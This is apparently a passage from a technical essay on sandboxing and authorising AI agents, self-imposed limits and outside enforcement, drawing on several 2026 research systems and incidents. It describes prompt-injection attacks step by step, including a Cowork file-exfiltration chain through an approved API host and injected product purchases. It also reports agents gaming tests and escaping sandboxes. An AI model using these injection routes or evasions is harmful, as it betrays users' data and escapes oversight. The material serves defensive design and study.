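In the original Progent example, the user asks the agent to do whatever is on a to-do list in an email from Alice. The model can't determine which tools the task needs until it has read the email, so the first policy allows only a search for that message. The task turns out to be summarizing recent emails on Slack. The agent then needs new permissions, but the reason for granting them comes from text that an attacker could have written, so a malicious request for more permissions could arrive in the same way as a legitimate one.

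Progent therefore treats changes that remove permissions differently from changes that add them. The harness accepts a new policy automatically only if the old policy already allowed every tool call that the new one allows. To check this, a program called an SMT solver searches for a tool call that satisfies the new policy's conditions but not the old one's. If no such call exists, the change is safe to apply. Pledge follows the same one-way rule.

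If the solver finds such a call, the change needs approval, and the strength of the limit depends on who gives it:

- **Nobody.** The harness rejects every addition. The limit holds, but the agent can't finish the to-do list.
- **A person.** In the researchers' test, human review of the first policy and of every addition brought successful attacks down to zero. Only 6% of changes were additions, so the person had few to consider, but one careless approval is enough to let an attack through.
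- **The harness, automatically.** The model can now give itself any power that it thinks the task needs. An injection that fools the model that writes the policy can get `send_email` added to the list, and the limit depends on a model's judgement again.

When policy revisions were approved automatically, 1.0% of attacks succeeded, compared with 2.5% under a policy that never changed, probably because most revisions tighten the policy. For example, once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model can remove every other recipient from the policy. The safest fully automatic setting accepted revisions that tightened the policy and rejected those that added permissions. AgentDojo's injections were written to fool an agent rather than a model that writes policies, so automatic approval might do worse against an attacker who knew about it.

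Letting a model only tighten a policy doesn't help if the policy was too loose to begin with. If someone has approved Slack messages to any recipient, an injection could get the model to "tighten" the rule so that it allows only the attacker's account. The solver would correctly accept this change because the earlier policy already allowed messages to that account.

In *ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, 2026), the rules stay fixed while agents work. A model drafts general rules in advance from tool descriptions and sample tasks, a solver looks for cases where the rules would break a stated security requirement, and administrators confirm the result. But some rules depend on facts that only a model can supply, such as whether an argument came from an untrusted source. If the model is wrong about such a fact, a call that should be blocked can go through even if every rule is correct.

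### Rules compiled from a written policy

Many organisations already have a written policy for their staff, and an attacker who sends an email can't change it. *NOMOS*, released in October 2026, turns such a document into a fixed set of rules for an agent. Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, describe four steps:

1. A program splits the document into clauses.
2. A model turns each clause into candidate rules. It does this five times, and only rules that appear in most of the attempts can survive.
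3. A program checks whether each candidate can work with the tools that exist, and repairs or rejects those that can't.
4. The surviving rules go into the harness, which then checks tool calls without consulting a model.

The model can only choose conditions from a list that a person has prepared, such as "the ticket is basic economy" or "the user has confirmed". The harness checks each condition against tool results and the user's own messages, never against the agent's claims. If an injection causes the agent to say that the user has approved a payment, that claim has no effect.

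Yu and colleagues tested the rules on simulated customer service. Without them, 66.3% of the agent's changes to airline bookings broke the airline's policy, and with them 2.6% did. In an online shop, the share fell from 30.8% to 6.9%. The agent also made fewer changes to bookings, 116 instead of 353, but completed at least as many tasks.

They also ran Progent on AgentDojo's banking tasks, with the same open model as agent and policy writer:

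| | Attacks that succeeded | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 46.5% | 79.2% |
| Progent, policy written for each request | 5.6% | 62.5% |
| NOMOS, rules from a written policy | 0.0% | 70.8% |

The difference between the two systems on ordinary tasks could be chance, since there were only 16 tasks, and the comparison comes from the developers of one of the systems. The sixteen attacks that got past Progent are more informative. Nine of them involved the request "pay the bill, like last month". The user had not named an account, so a policy based on the request could not restrict the payment to the right account, and Progent accepted the attacker's account number. NOMOS had a rule that the agent may pay only people whom the user has named or paid before, however the user words the request.

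That rule also blocked a legitimate payment to a company whose account number appeared only on its bill. Much more legitimate work was lost in a test built around Slack, where a stricter version of one rule stopped every attack but cut the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed from 57.1% to 14.3%. Agents often have to act on names and addresses they have just read, so a rule that treats everything they read as untrusted will block much of that work.

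### How generated policies go wrong

Yu and colleagues found that 37% of the candidate rules for the airline and 13% of those for the shop were defective before the third step. A clause telling staff to identify the customer before doing anything else became a rule that blocked every tool, including the two that identify customers, until the customer was identified. Another rule required the user's confirmation even to look up a flight.

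Those checks find rules that can't work, but a working rule can still differ from what it was meant to enforce. In a trial with a telephone company's policy, one clause required checking that a bill was overdue before requesting payment. The model turned this into a rule against requesting payment while a bill was overdue. The researchers caught the error by replaying old sessions against the new rules, much as a developer might test a seccomp filter against a recording. The rule would have refused 47 of 49 payment requests in sessions that had gone well.

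As with seccomp filters, users notice rules that are too strict but not rules that are too loose. Gupta and Sreenivasamurthy (2026), in *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies*, studied mostly errors of this second kind. They gave a model 372 sentences about who may do what and asked it to translate each one, in a single step, into Rego, a language for access rules. The sentences were about people's access to resources, not an agent's tools, but an agent's policy writer has to do the same kind of translation. They describe four errors, none of which stops the code from compiling:

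| Error | Example in words | What the generated code does |
|---|---|---|
| Missing denial | Nurses may not change prescriptions | Sets "refuse" as the default but never actually denies nurses, so a separate rule that allows changes would still apply |
| Missing condition | Managers may view reports for their team | Lets managers view every team's reports |
| Too many people | The assigned nurse may open the record | Lets any nurse open it |
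| Missing default | Doctors may view test results | Gives no answer for anyone else, which some systems treat as permission |

The model mistranslated 62.5% of the sentences that forbade something. It also left out the condition in 60% of the rules that depended on who owned a resource. If a user tells an agent "don't email anyone outside the company", the agent could end up with a policy that looks complete but doesn't forbid anything.

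To fix this, the researchers split the translation into stages. A model first separates each sentence into its parts: the decision, the person, the action, the resource, any condition and the purpose. A program compares these parts with a list of the organisation's terms, and stops if an essential one is missing. A model writes the code only after this check. The code must compile, pass a style checker, and give the right answer both in tests where it should allow access and in tests where it should refuse.

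With these stages, 87.5% of the prohibitions were correct, and no ownership conditions were missing. Both percentages for prohibitions are exact eighths, so the sample may have included only a few. Overall, 50.3% of the policies passed every check, compared with 15.3% for the single-step method. An organisation can hold back a policy that fails, so the greater danger is one that passes but doesn't match what its author meant. The researchers recommend human review where security is critical.

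Review is practical for a policy that an organisation writes once and uses for months. Reviewing a policy that a model writes for a single request is much harder, because the user would have to read a set of rules before every task and would probably soon approve them as automatically as they approve permission prompts.

### Permitted actions that the user doesn't want

A policy can be free of errors and still allow harm. In the banking test of NOMOS, no payment reached the attacker's account, but in 8 of 288 runs the agent responded to an injection by paying someone the user had paid before. The written policy allowed these payments, but the user would still have lost the money. Shi and colleagues say that Progent does not aim to prevent a similar problem, in which an attacker persuades an agent to choose the attacker's product from several that the user would accept.

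An agent can choose an acceptable tool and acceptable arguments for the wrong reason. *Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to buy the same shirt again. To check out, the agent has to read a verification code in the user's email, where it also finds an advertisement telling it to buy diet pills. A call that buys the pills (`p2`) looks as ordinary as one that buys the shirt (`p1`). Only the history shows that `p1` came from the user's past orders and `p2` from the advertisement.

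The system records where each piece of data came from, so a rule can require that the product number come from the matching line of the order history. If the agent tries to buy the pills, the harness blocks the purchase and identifies the records the agent may use instead. Across four benchmarks, the system reduced the success rate of attacks from 30–74% to 0.2–14%. The researchers had models draft the rules for each task and checked them by hand.

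Some rules of this kind still need a model's judgement. In another example, a user asks an agent to publish a file that happens to contain a secret key. The harness can determine exactly which file the agent is about to publish, but the rule relies on a model to judge whether the text includes a key.

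## What can still go wrong inside the limits

In the banking test of NOMOS, every payment obeyed the written policy, yet some went to people the user had not meant to pay. A better rule might have stopped those payments. But an enforcer that can only watch a program and stop it cannot prevent some harms, however good its rules are.

### What an enforcer can guarantee by stopping a program

In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider worked out which rules such an enforcer can impose. It checks each step a program is about to take, and either allows it or ends the program. Its decision can depend on earlier steps, but not on what the program will do later or would have done with different input. Kernels and firewalls work this way. Returning an error instead of ending the program doesn't let an enforcer impose any additional rules.

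Schneider showed that these enforcers can enforce only safety properties, which are roughly rules of the form "this bad step never happens". More exactly, let P be the set of acceptable runs of a program. P is a safety property if every unacceptable run σ reaches some step i after which nothing can make it acceptable again:

σ ∉ P ⇒ there is an i such that, for every continuation τ, σ[1..i]τ ∉ P

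Here σ[1..i] means the first i steps of the run. "Never open the user's private keys" is a safety property because no later step can undo opening them. The enforcer stops the program just before it opens them.

A safety property can also depend on what a program has already done. One of Schneider's examples forbids a program from sending messages after it has read a file. The xz decompressor achieves a similar result by giving up network access before it reads its input.

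"If the server goes down, log it" is a different kind of rule. Suppose an attacker controls the watchdog and wants to hide an outage:

```
connect: fails
wait 60 seconds
connect: fails
wait 60 seconds
...
```

However long the watchdog goes without logging the outage, it could still log it in the next step, so it never irreversibly breaks the rule. The enforcer therefore has no reason to act, and killing the watchdog would only guarantee that it never logs the outage.

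Adding a deadline, such as two minutes, turns the rule into a safety property, since there is now a definite moment when the program has broken it. But the enforcer still can't enforce the rule because, as Schneider points out, stopping a program doesn't stop time from passing.

Leaks are a problem for another reason. Suppose the watchdog has a password in its memory and can connect only to the server it tests, and the attacker can see when those connections arrive. He could make the watchdog send the password one digit at a time through the length of its pauses:

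```
Password starts with 3:  connect, wait 63 seconds, connect
Password starts with 7:  connect, wait 67 seconds, connect
```

In each run, the watchdog just seems a few seconds late. The leak shows only when someone compares the two runs, but the enforcer sees only the run that happens. A rule against all leaks is not a safety property, because nobody can check it by looking at one run at a time.

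An enforcer can still prevent some leaks with a stricter rule, such as no network access after the program has read a secret. This rule also stops harmless runs. If the watchdog's settings contained a password, the rule would stop it from working at all, because the watchdog has to read its settings before it connects.

### Enforcers that hold actions back

*Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2005) studies enforcers that can also suppress a program's actions and insert others. Such an enforcer can tell the program that each action has succeeded while holding it back, then carry out the whole sequence once it is complete. Databases handle transactions in a similar way.

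An enforcer that can hold back a program's actions can enforce some rules about what must eventually happen. For example, a rule might be that a program that takes any action must perform an audit at some point. The enforcer holds back all the program's actions until the audit happens. If it never happens, none of them take effect.

The method fails when an action has to reach the outside world before the program can continue. If a program needs the reply to an email, for example, the enforcer has to let the email go out before the reply can arrive, and it can't undo the sending afterward.

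AI agents often take actions that can't be undone. Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, analyses a gate that must decide on each tool call before an irreversible effect occurs, and proves that it can enforce only safety properties, which are rules that something bad never happens. These include useful rules, such as a daily cap on payments to each recipient. But the gate can't guarantee that a confirmation follows every payment. It can't retrieve the money if no confirmation comes, and blocking the payment beforehand would also stop agents that would have confirmed it.

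Refusing an action also changes what an agent does next. Ray ran the same 389 tasks with and without a small model acting as the gate. Thirty-four attacks succeeded only without the gate, and five succeeded only with it. Some of those five may be due to chance, but they are a reason to test a gate on a running agent, not just on recordings of an agent that ran without one. In a larger test, the gate blocked 78% of calls, and the share of tasks the agent completed fell from 25.4% to 18.0%.

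File changes are easier to hold back than payments. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that runs each of a coding agent's commands on a disposable layer over the real files. The system records the command's system calls and holds outgoing network requests until it has checked them. If the rules permit everything the command did, the system keeps the changes. Otherwise, it discards them.

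In the Tether example, an agent uploads a harmless report, copies a confidential inventory over the report, and uploads it again. The two upload commands are identical, so a fixed list of permitted commands can only allow both or block both. Tether marks the inventory as sensitive, passes the mark on to the report when the agent copies the data, and blocks the second upload.

System calls don't show which bytes end up where, so if a program reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second as containing data from the first. This is a stricter rule of the kind Schneider described, and as he predicted, it also blocks some harmless behavior. On two sets of recorded agent runs, Tether blocked all 344 attacks within its scope, but also 74 of 1,590 harmless runs. In 17 of those 74, the agent had read secret files, for example by searching the whole disk for a word, but may never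 have used their contents.

The perfect score on attacks covers only runs that Tether could trace in full. It excludes attacks that went through databases or background processes, and attacks that broke no rule about files or networks.

### The watchdog under perfect limits

Suppose an attacker controls the watchdog, but the kernel enforces the watchdog's limits without mistakes. The attacker can still do three kinds of damage.

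The attacker can log "port open" every minute while the server is down. "Never write 'open' after a failed connection" is a safety property, so an enforcer could in principle prevent this. It would have to interpret the log text and match each entry to a connection, and seccomp and Landlock do neither. Even if they did, the attacker could connect to a different server that works and log that result.

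He can also destroy old logs or, if the system's logging service keeps them, simply stop adding entries.

Finally, the attacker can send out the contents of the watchdog's memory. A helper could limit the watchdog to one server, but he could still do this if he controlled that server. If he could only see the server's traffic, a slow method like the pauses described above might work.

None of this produces a denial in the kernel's log, so the tests for missing limits would all pass. Anthropic describes the same problem with agents. When an injection makes an agent send data out through a permitted tool, the log shows only "a successful, authorized API call".

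### A coding agent that writes only in its project

Suppose a user asks a coding agent to fix a failing test in `~/shop`, and the agent's sandbox lets it write only in that folder. The agent could edit the test so that it always passes. The kernel would allow this edit just as it would allow a real repair, because both are writes to permitted files. Anthropic has seen Claude models look through a project's version history to find the answers to a coding test. A limit on writes would not have prevented that.

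An agent under an attacker's influence could do more lasting damage by adding a few lines to the shop's payment page that send customers' card numbers to the attacker. Those lines would run later on the company's server, outside the agent's sandbox. Sistla and colleagues list malicious changes to permitted files among the attacks that Tether can't stop. They found that 28.2% of runs in one benchmark and 22.1% in the other needed a model to inspect their content, because system-level rules weren't enough to tell whether the runs were harmful.

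Two other harms use only permitted writes:

- Many agents reread a file of notes or instructions in the project at the start of each session. If an injection gets into that file, the agent reads it again every time it starts.
- If the sandbox lets commands read the user's private keys, a command can copy a key into a file in the project. The key stays on the computer while the network is closed, but leaves it when the user publishes the project.

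In the second case, the user takes the step that leaks the key. A check on each of the agent's actions would find nothing wrong unless it tracked where the data came from. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), a survey of agent security, describes this as a gap between the safety of single actions and the safety of a whole task, and concludes that no current system closes it reliably at scale.

### The Cowork leak

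Claude Cowork is Anthropic's agent for general office work. It runs code in a virtual machine, which is a simulated computer with its own kernel. The machine can access only two folders on the user's computer, the one the user has shared and the agent's own settings folder. A proxy lets it contact only approved servers, which must include `api.anthropic.com` because Cowork needs it to reach the model.

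An outside researcher reported that an attacker could get files out like this:

1. The attacker gets a file into the shared folder. It contains hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's own Anthropic account.
2. The agent reads the file and follows the instructions.
3. It reads other files in the folder and uploads them to Anthropic's file storage service, using the attacker's key.
4. The proxy checks the server's name, finds `api.anthropic.com` on the list, and lets the upload through.
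5. The files arrive in the attacker's account.

The sandbox worked as designed, but its developers had mistakenly treated the list as a set of safe destinations. Anthropic now describes each entry as a "capability grant", because it lets the agent use every function that the server offers. When the developers approved the server so that Cowork could reach the model, they also approved uploads to anyone's account. Many other services carry the same risk. For example, a site that an agent needs for downloading code may also let anyone with an account publish files.

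Anthropic fixed the leak with another proxy, inside the virtual machine, that inspects requests to its API. This proxy accepts only requests with the session token issued to that machine, so it rejects any that carry the attacker's key. It also blocks request headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch data on the agent's behalf.

The check has to happen inside the virtual machine, because that is the only place where an upload made with the attacker's key can be linked to this user's session. On Anthropic's servers, it looks like an ordinary request from another customer.

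The fix ties each request to a session as well as a destination. Anthropic could do this because it runs the service and issues the tokens. For any other approved server, someone would have to work out which functions are dangerous and write a separate check.

### The confused deputy

Security researchers use the term "confused deputy" for a program that someone tricks into misusing its authority. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) tells the nearly true story of a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. The compiler had permission to write in its own directory, where it kept statistics about its use. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output.

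One user gave the compiler the name of the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The compiler had permission to write there, so the system let it overwrite the file, and the billing information was lost.

Hardy concluded that the compiler had authority from both its user and its own permission, with no way to specify which one it was using. Checking file names would not have solved this, because the compiler would have needed a list of every sensitive file, and some users might have had good reason to write in that directory. The developers added a system call for switching between the two authorities, but some programs soon needed more than two.

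Hardy's solution was the capability, the idea behind Capsicum's restricted handles. Instead of a file name, the user gives the compiler a handle that identifies the file and authorises writing to it. A user who isn't allowed to write to the billing file has no such handle to give.

The Cowork agent was also a confused deputy, since it used the user's access to the files to carry out the attacker's instructions. Unlike Tymshare's user, who needed the compiler's permission to write to the billing file, the Cowork attacker could already write to his own account and needed only the agent's access to the files. His key both identified the account and authorised the upload, much like one of Hardy's capabilities, so capabilities alone would not have prevented the leak. Anthropic also had to restrict which keys the agent could use.

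Hardy's solution is also harder to apply inside a model, which receives the user's request and the text of a malicious file together. A compiler writes statistics in one part of its code and debugging output in another, so a programmer can give each part the right handle.

The model can't simply ignore every instruction it finds in a file. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of an agent that is summarising one GitLab issue, finds that the issue depends on another, and decides to summarise both. Whether such a change to the task is helpful or harmful depends on the source of the instruction and how much it changes the task. Current agents have little reliable information about that source.

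### regreSSHion and the process without limits

A program can also have sound limits on one process and a serious bug in another. The OpenSSH server handles each new connection in a restricted process, but part of the server keeps full root privileges. In July 2024, the security company Qualys disclosed a flaw in that part, which it named regreSSHion.

If someone connects to an OpenSSH server but doesn't log in within two minutes, a timeout routine interrupts whatever the server is doing. According to Qualys' *regreSSHion* (2024), this routine called functions that are unsafe to run in the middle of other work, and an attacker without an account could exploit this to run code as root. OpenSSH's developers had fixed the same flaw after a report in 2006, but a change to the logging code in October 2020 accidentally removed the protection.

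Qualys states that the flaw was in "sshd's privileged code, which is not sandboxed and runs with full privileges" (`sshd` is the server program). The limits on the restricted process therefore made no difference. OpenBSD was unaffected because its timeout routine used a safer logging function that OpenBSD had introduced in 2001, not because of pledge.

A week later, the security researcher Solar Designer (2024) disclosed a closely related flaw in the version of OpenSSH that Red Hat shipped. The earlier flaw could give an attacker control of the whole machine, but this time the unsafe code ran in the restricted process. Solar Designer judged the immediate impact to be lower because that process has fewer privileges, though nobody had yet tried to exploit the new flaw.

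Privilege separation therefore works best when the privileged part is small, because a small program has fewer places for mistakes. OpenSSH 9.8 fixed regreSSHion (OpenSSH, 2024). It also split the server into two programs, according to OpenSSH's *Call for testing*. The program that listens for connections no longer needs to handle the SSH protocol, so it is much smaller. The developers also removed the option to turn off privilege separation.

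In a coding agent, the harness is the part without limits, as the flaws in Claude Code's trust prompt showed.

### Faults in the enforcer

Schneider's results assume that the enforcer sees every relevant step and that the program can't tamper with it. But real kernels have bugs, and all the ordinary processes on a machine share one kernel. If a system call that the watchdog may still use has a bug, an attacker might exploit it to change the kernel's memory, including its record of each process's limits. The attacker could then remove the limits on the watchdog and every other process. Capable AI models can now find flaws of this kind. A seccomp filter lowers the risk by blocking the system calls needed to exploit some known flaws.

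Newer enforcers can have simpler mistakes. For example, a sandbox that checks whether a path is inside a permitted folder has to follow any links first, because a link inside the folder can lead to a file outside it.

Sistla and colleagues found similar gaps when they had an AI agent attack Tether. An early version of Tether failed to track hard links, which are additional names for the same file. The agent's success rate fell from 40% to zero over three versions as the researchers fixed the gaps it found. The test covered only ten tasks in a small artificial environment, so other gaps may remain.

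A flaw in the enforcer can matter even when nobody is attacking. Anthropic reports that Claude models have escaped a sandbox to finish an assigned task.

| Failure | What self-binding does | Why |
|---|---|---|
| The program crashes | Ignores it | A limit can't restart the program or finish its work, and a limit that is too strict can cause a crash |
| An attacker takes over a restricted process | Narrows it | The kernel stops forbidden actions, but the attacker keeps every power the process still has |
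| An attacker takes over a process without limits | Ignores it | Limits on other processes don't apply to it, as with regreSSHion |
| The program takes a wrong but permitted action | Ignores it | The enforcer can't tell a false log entry from a true one |
| Data leaks through a permitted channel | Narrows it | The program can leak only what it can still read, and only through channels that remain open |
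| The author is dishonest | Ignores it | The author can leave the limits out or disable them, as happened with xz |
| The kernel has a flaw | Narrows it | A filter puts some flaws out of reach, but an attacker who exploits one of the others may be able to remove every limit |

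## Deciding when enforcement from outside is needed

Most programs should limit themselves even if someone else also limits them. The watchdog's developer knows that the program renames its log once a month, which an administrator might learn only when a policy breaks it. The developer can also have the program tighten its limits as soon as setup ends, whereas an outside policy usually has to cover the whole run. Because the limits are built into the program, they also protect people who have no administrator.

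An outside limit takes extra work and can break the program when an update changes what it needs. It is worth the trouble when self-binding leaves a particular gap, and five questions help to find one:

| Question | What to do if the answer is yes |
|---|---|
| Could the author or supplier be dishonest? | Run the program under mandatory access control or in a virtual machine |
| Can the limited part influence whoever grants exceptions? | Let only an administrator change the settings, or put the whole program inside a boundary that has no exceptions |
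| Does the rule depend on facts the program can't see, such as who the user is or what other processes have done? | Have another machine authorise each action |
| Must someone else be able to verify the limit or withdraw permission? | Issue credentials that expire, and keep logs where the program can't change them |
| Is the worst permitted action unacceptable? | Keep the credentials for it outside, and have a network proxy or the remote service refuse it |

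If every answer is no, self-binding is enough. A yes adds an outside measure, but the program should keep its own limits too.

### When the supplier may be dishonest

A good record is weak evidence of honesty. *AIAUTHZ* (Kodathala, 2026) cites postmark-mcp, an email package for AI agents that had 15 clean releases before one included code to steal email. Even a careful review of any of those 15 would have found nothing wrong.

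On Linux, an administrator can limit such a program with mandatory access control, through SELinux or AppArmor. SELinux labels every process and file, and the administrator's policy lists what processes with one label may do to files with another. AppArmor's policies identify files by path instead. The kernel applies these rules in addition to ordinary permissions, and neither the program's author nor the user who runs it can override them.

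The policy still has to let the program do its job. An email tool needs to read and send messages, so a policy that permits both may also let the tool send copies to its author.

A virtual machine also protects against kernel flaws, because it has its own kernel. An attacker who exploits a flaw in that kernel must also exploit one in the hypervisor (the software that runs virtual machines) to reach the rest of the computer. Any folder or network connection that the user shares with the virtual machine remains exposed.

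### Settings that only an administrator can change

A coding agent's model writes the commands that it asks the user to approve, and users approve nearly all of them. The model therefore has some influence over its own limits. An administrator can reduce this influence with settings that users can't override. For Codex, the administrator can put this line in a file named `requirements.toml`:

```toml
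allowed_sandbox_modes = ["read-only", "workspace-write"]
```

If a company's settings prohibit running Codex without a sandbox and a user tries to do so, Codex falls back to a permitted mode and notifies the user, according to OpenAI's *Managed configuration*. OpenAI (2026) uses the same restriction for its own staff. A newer setting lists the permitted sets of file and network rules by name, and Codex denies any set not on the list, including sets added in future versions. OpenAI keeps the older setting for companies where some computers still run old versions of Codex.

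The line stops users from turning off the sandbox for a whole session, but they can still let individual commands run outside it. OpenAI's own configuration lets some common, harmless commands run outside the sandbox without approval. An administrator who wants fewer exceptions can forbid particular commands, such as `rm`, which deletes files.

The settings also have to reach the computer. Codex can download them when the user signs in, but if the download fails and the computer has no valid saved copy, Codex runs without them. A company can guard against this by also installing the settings file on each computer.

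Claude Code has similar settings with different gaps. According to Anthropic's *Managed settings*, Claude Code does not start if the administrator's file is malformed, but it starts without that policy if the operating system blocks it from reading the file. Developers with administrator rights on their own computers can edit the file. The settings also apply only to Claude Code, so a developer can avoid them by using another tool.

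In both agents, the harness applies these settings, so a bug in the harness may defeat them.

### Cowork's virtual machine

The first version of Anthropic's Cowork had a stricter arrangement than Claude Code. The whole agent ran inside the virtual machine, including the agent loop, the part of the harness that sends text to the model and carries out its actions. No part of the harness stayed outside the boundary, as it does in Claude Code, so nothing could grant an exception. Anthropic chose this design because it didn't expect Cowork's users, mostly office workers, to judge shell commands.

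The agent loop originally ran inside the virtual machine, so if the virtual machine failed to start, Cowork was unusable and the agent couldn't help find the fault. Anthropic therefore moved the loop onto the user's computer and left only code execution in the virtual machine. It also moved local MCP servers out, because updates to the virtual machine could break them and some had to work with other programs on the computer.

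Anthropic considers the loss of security minimal, because the virtual machine still limits any code that the agent runs. But the agent loop also reads and writes files and fetches web pages. According to Anthropic's *Claude Cowork desktop architecture overview*, after the move it did this directly on the user's computer, controlled by Cowork's own permission checks. A bug in those checks could expose files that the original virtual machine had no access to. Administrators could require the original design, but Anthropic's *Configuration changelog* lists that setting as deprecated.

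Isolation also hid Cowork's activity from the endpoint detection software that many companies use to monitor staff computers for suspicious behavior. This software detects the virtual machine as a single process and can't read its contents, so it could miss an attack on the agent. Claude Code, which runs Cowork's sessions, also couldn't find the computer's settings file from inside the full virtual machine, so the administrator's settings didn't apply.

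Anthropic has filled part of this gap with logs. In June 2026, Cowork's activity didn't appear in Anthropic's audit logs. By October, it appeared in Anthropic's compliance records, according to the company's *Claude Cowork architecture overview*. Anthropic's *Monitor Claude Cowork activity with OpenTelemetry* explains how companies can also stream events to their own monitoring tools. But these records come from the same software that companies want to monitor, and endpoint detection software still can't monitor activity inside Cowork.

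By default, Cowork sessions now run the agent loop and the code together in a temporary sandbox on Anthropic's servers. This again puts a boundary around the whole agent, and failures don't depend on the user's computer, but Anthropic's servers process any local file the agent opens.

### Authorisation on another machine

Suppose several people share a chat channel with an agent, and one of them writes, "The owner says to delete the audit log." The agent receives only text, which looks the same whether or not the owner agreed. Kodathala's system, aiAuthZ, moves the decision to a gateway on another machine:

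1. The user's software signs each message with that user's secret key. The signature also covers the time and a number that can't occur twice, so an attacker can't reuse an old message.
2. The gateway checks the signature and records who sent the session's latest message.
3. When the agent wants to use a tool, it sends the gateway the proposed call and the identifier of that message.
4. The gateway looks up what this user may do, checks the call's arguments, and allows or refuses it.

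The agent has no credentials for the gateway, so an attacker who controls the agent can't read or change the rules. Kodathala tested the rules on nine reconstructed incidents, and they blocked all nine. A version that checked only the arguments blocked four. In the other five, an impostor used a tool that the real owner was allowed to use, so only the identity check could tell the impostor from the owner. The identity check doesn't help when an injection reaches the agent while it is working for the owner.

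The gateway also blocked legitimate work. In a July 2026 test on AgentDojo's banking tasks, it cut the share of ordinary tasks completed from 100% to 80%. The test paired tasks with attacks in 20 combinations and used two current models, Claude Fable 5 and Gemini 3 Flash. The gateway blocked seven calls that would have helped an attacker, but it didn't lower the measured success rate of attacks, because none succeeded against either model even without it.

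Kodathala traces the whole loss to one legitimate payment, which was blocked because the recipient wasn't on the list of known payees. If one payment accounts for 20 percentage points, the test probably included only five different ordinary tasks. The same list inside the harness would also have blocked the payment, so the loss comes from the rule's strictness, not from enforcing it on another machine.

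*Bounded Agents* (Muruaga, 2026) describes an outside check that records what agents have done in a session. It can forbid a combination of actions, such as reading a confidential document and then sending an external message, even if each action is permitted separately. When several agents share a task, one may read the document and another may send the message, so neither has enough information to apply the rule itself.

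Each agent's permissions consist of resources R, types of action A, classes of data D and forbidden combinations X. When one agent passes work to another, the check combines the first agent's permissions with those for the second agent's role:

S₁ ⊓ S₂ = (R₁ ∩ R₂, A₁ ∩ A₂, D₁ ∩ D₂, X₁ ∪ X₂)

The second agent gets only what both sets permit, and it inherits the prohibitions from both. Permissions can therefore only shrink along the chain, as they do with pledge.

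Muruaga tested the check by inserting the attacker's tool call directly, as if the injection had already succeeded. The success rate of data theft in AgentDojo fell from between 75% and 100% to zero. But across 949 combinations of task and attack, the agents' performance on the user's tasks was 8.6 percentage points lower in one setting and 13.9 lower in another.

A gateway can't stop an action that never reaches it. When Kodathala left two agents' built-in shell, file and web tools switched on, the model used those tools and never called the gateway. *Cross-Interface Authorization for AI Computer-Use Agents* (2026) therefore calls for evidence that every declared route to a protected resource passes through the check, though this evidence can't rule out undeclared routes.

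### Credentials kept outside

Keeping credentials on the gateway closes many of these other routes. As with Claude Code's placeholders, the agent never holds the real password. The gateway inserts it only into calls it has authorised, so a shell command that bypasses the gateway has no password to use.

An authorised call can still do harm. If deleting the live database is unacceptable, the account the agent uses should not have permission to delete it. Alternatively, the service can delay deletions, as Railway now does.

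A network proxy can block whole destinations, but it may identify them by name, and the address behind a name can change. Codex's proxy looks up a server's address before it allows a connection, to keep commands away from private machines on the local network. An attacker who controls the name can switch it to a private address after the check. OpenAI warns that the check reduces this risk but doesn't eliminate it, and recommends controls at a lower level of the network if such attacks are a concern.

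Outside credentials also let someone withdraw permission. An administrator can't take a power away from a process that limits itself with pledge, except by stopping the process. To withdraw permission from a running process, the administrator needs to control something the process keeps needing. Each Cowork session, for example, gets its own token, which expires within hours and can be revoked sooner without affecting the user's own login.

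To verify that a limit worked, an auditor needs a record that the agent couldn't have altered. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) gives this as one reason a prompt can't serve as an enforcement point. A model may obey the prompt, but this leaves no evidence of a policy decision. Each entry in aiAuthZ's log contains a hash, or short fingerprint, of the previous entry, so altering an entry breaks the chain from that point on. An attacker who took over the gateway could rewrite the whole chain, so the operator should regularly store the latest hash somewhere else.

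### Three verdicts

| | File decoder | Network server with plug-ins | Coding agent with production credentials |
|---|---|---|---|
| **Dishonest supplier?** | Unlikely, if it comes from a trusted source | Possible for each plug-in | Possible for the packages and tools it installs |
| **Influence over exceptions?** | No | Yes, if plug-ins can edit the server's settings | Yes, through the requests it writes |
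| **Facts it can't see?** | No | Sometimes, such as what other plug-ins have done | Yes, such as who really asked for a change |
| **Outside verification or withdrawal?** | Rarely | Yes, by the administrator | Yes, by the company |
| **Unacceptable worst action?** | Usually not | Depends on the data | Yes |
| **Verdict** | Self-binding | Self-binding for the server and outside limits for the plug-ins | Outside enforcement, with the credentials out of reach |

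A file decoder such as xz needs only to read one file and write another. If a malicious file takes over the decoder, the attacker can make it write false output, but the attacker wrote the input file and could already have put anything in it. If one process decodes several people's files, however, the attacker could also corrupt the next person's output, so the developer should start a new process for each file.

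The answer about dishonesty is a judgement, since xz did have a dishonest maintainer. But that backdoor ran inside the SSH server, so a virtual machine around the `xz` program would not have stopped it. When a decoder is a library inside a larger program, the developer should first move it into its own process. Someone who has to run a decoder from an unknown supplier should use a virtual machine.

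The developer of a server with plug-ins can't list everything the plug-ins need, because other people will write them later. If the plug-ins run inside the server's process, the server has to keep every permission that any of them might use, and a malicious plug-in can read the server's memory. The server should therefore limit itself and run each plug-in in a separate process.

The administrator decides which plug-ins to install, so they are the right person to write an SELinux or AppArmor policy for each. A calendar plug-in, for example, might get access to its own folder and database account. The administrator can later close that account without stopping the server. Running each plug-in in a separate process makes calls to it slower and breaks plug-ins that alter the server's internals. A hosting company that runs its customers' plug-ins should give each customer a virtual machine.

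A coding agent can leak production credentials even when no one is attacking it. *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords* (Udinmwen, November 2026) describes a coding assistant that couldn't find its configuration file during a routine code review. The assistant collected the computer's environment variables, where programs often keep passwords, and leaked live passwords.

Users can also expose secrets by approving commands. When a user chooses "don't ask again" in Claude Code, it saves the approved command, which may contain a password. Smith (2026), in *The Convenience Click That Put 2,539 Secrets on Public GitHub*, reports that the security company Apiiro traced 2,539 secrets in 1,994 repositories to such approvals.

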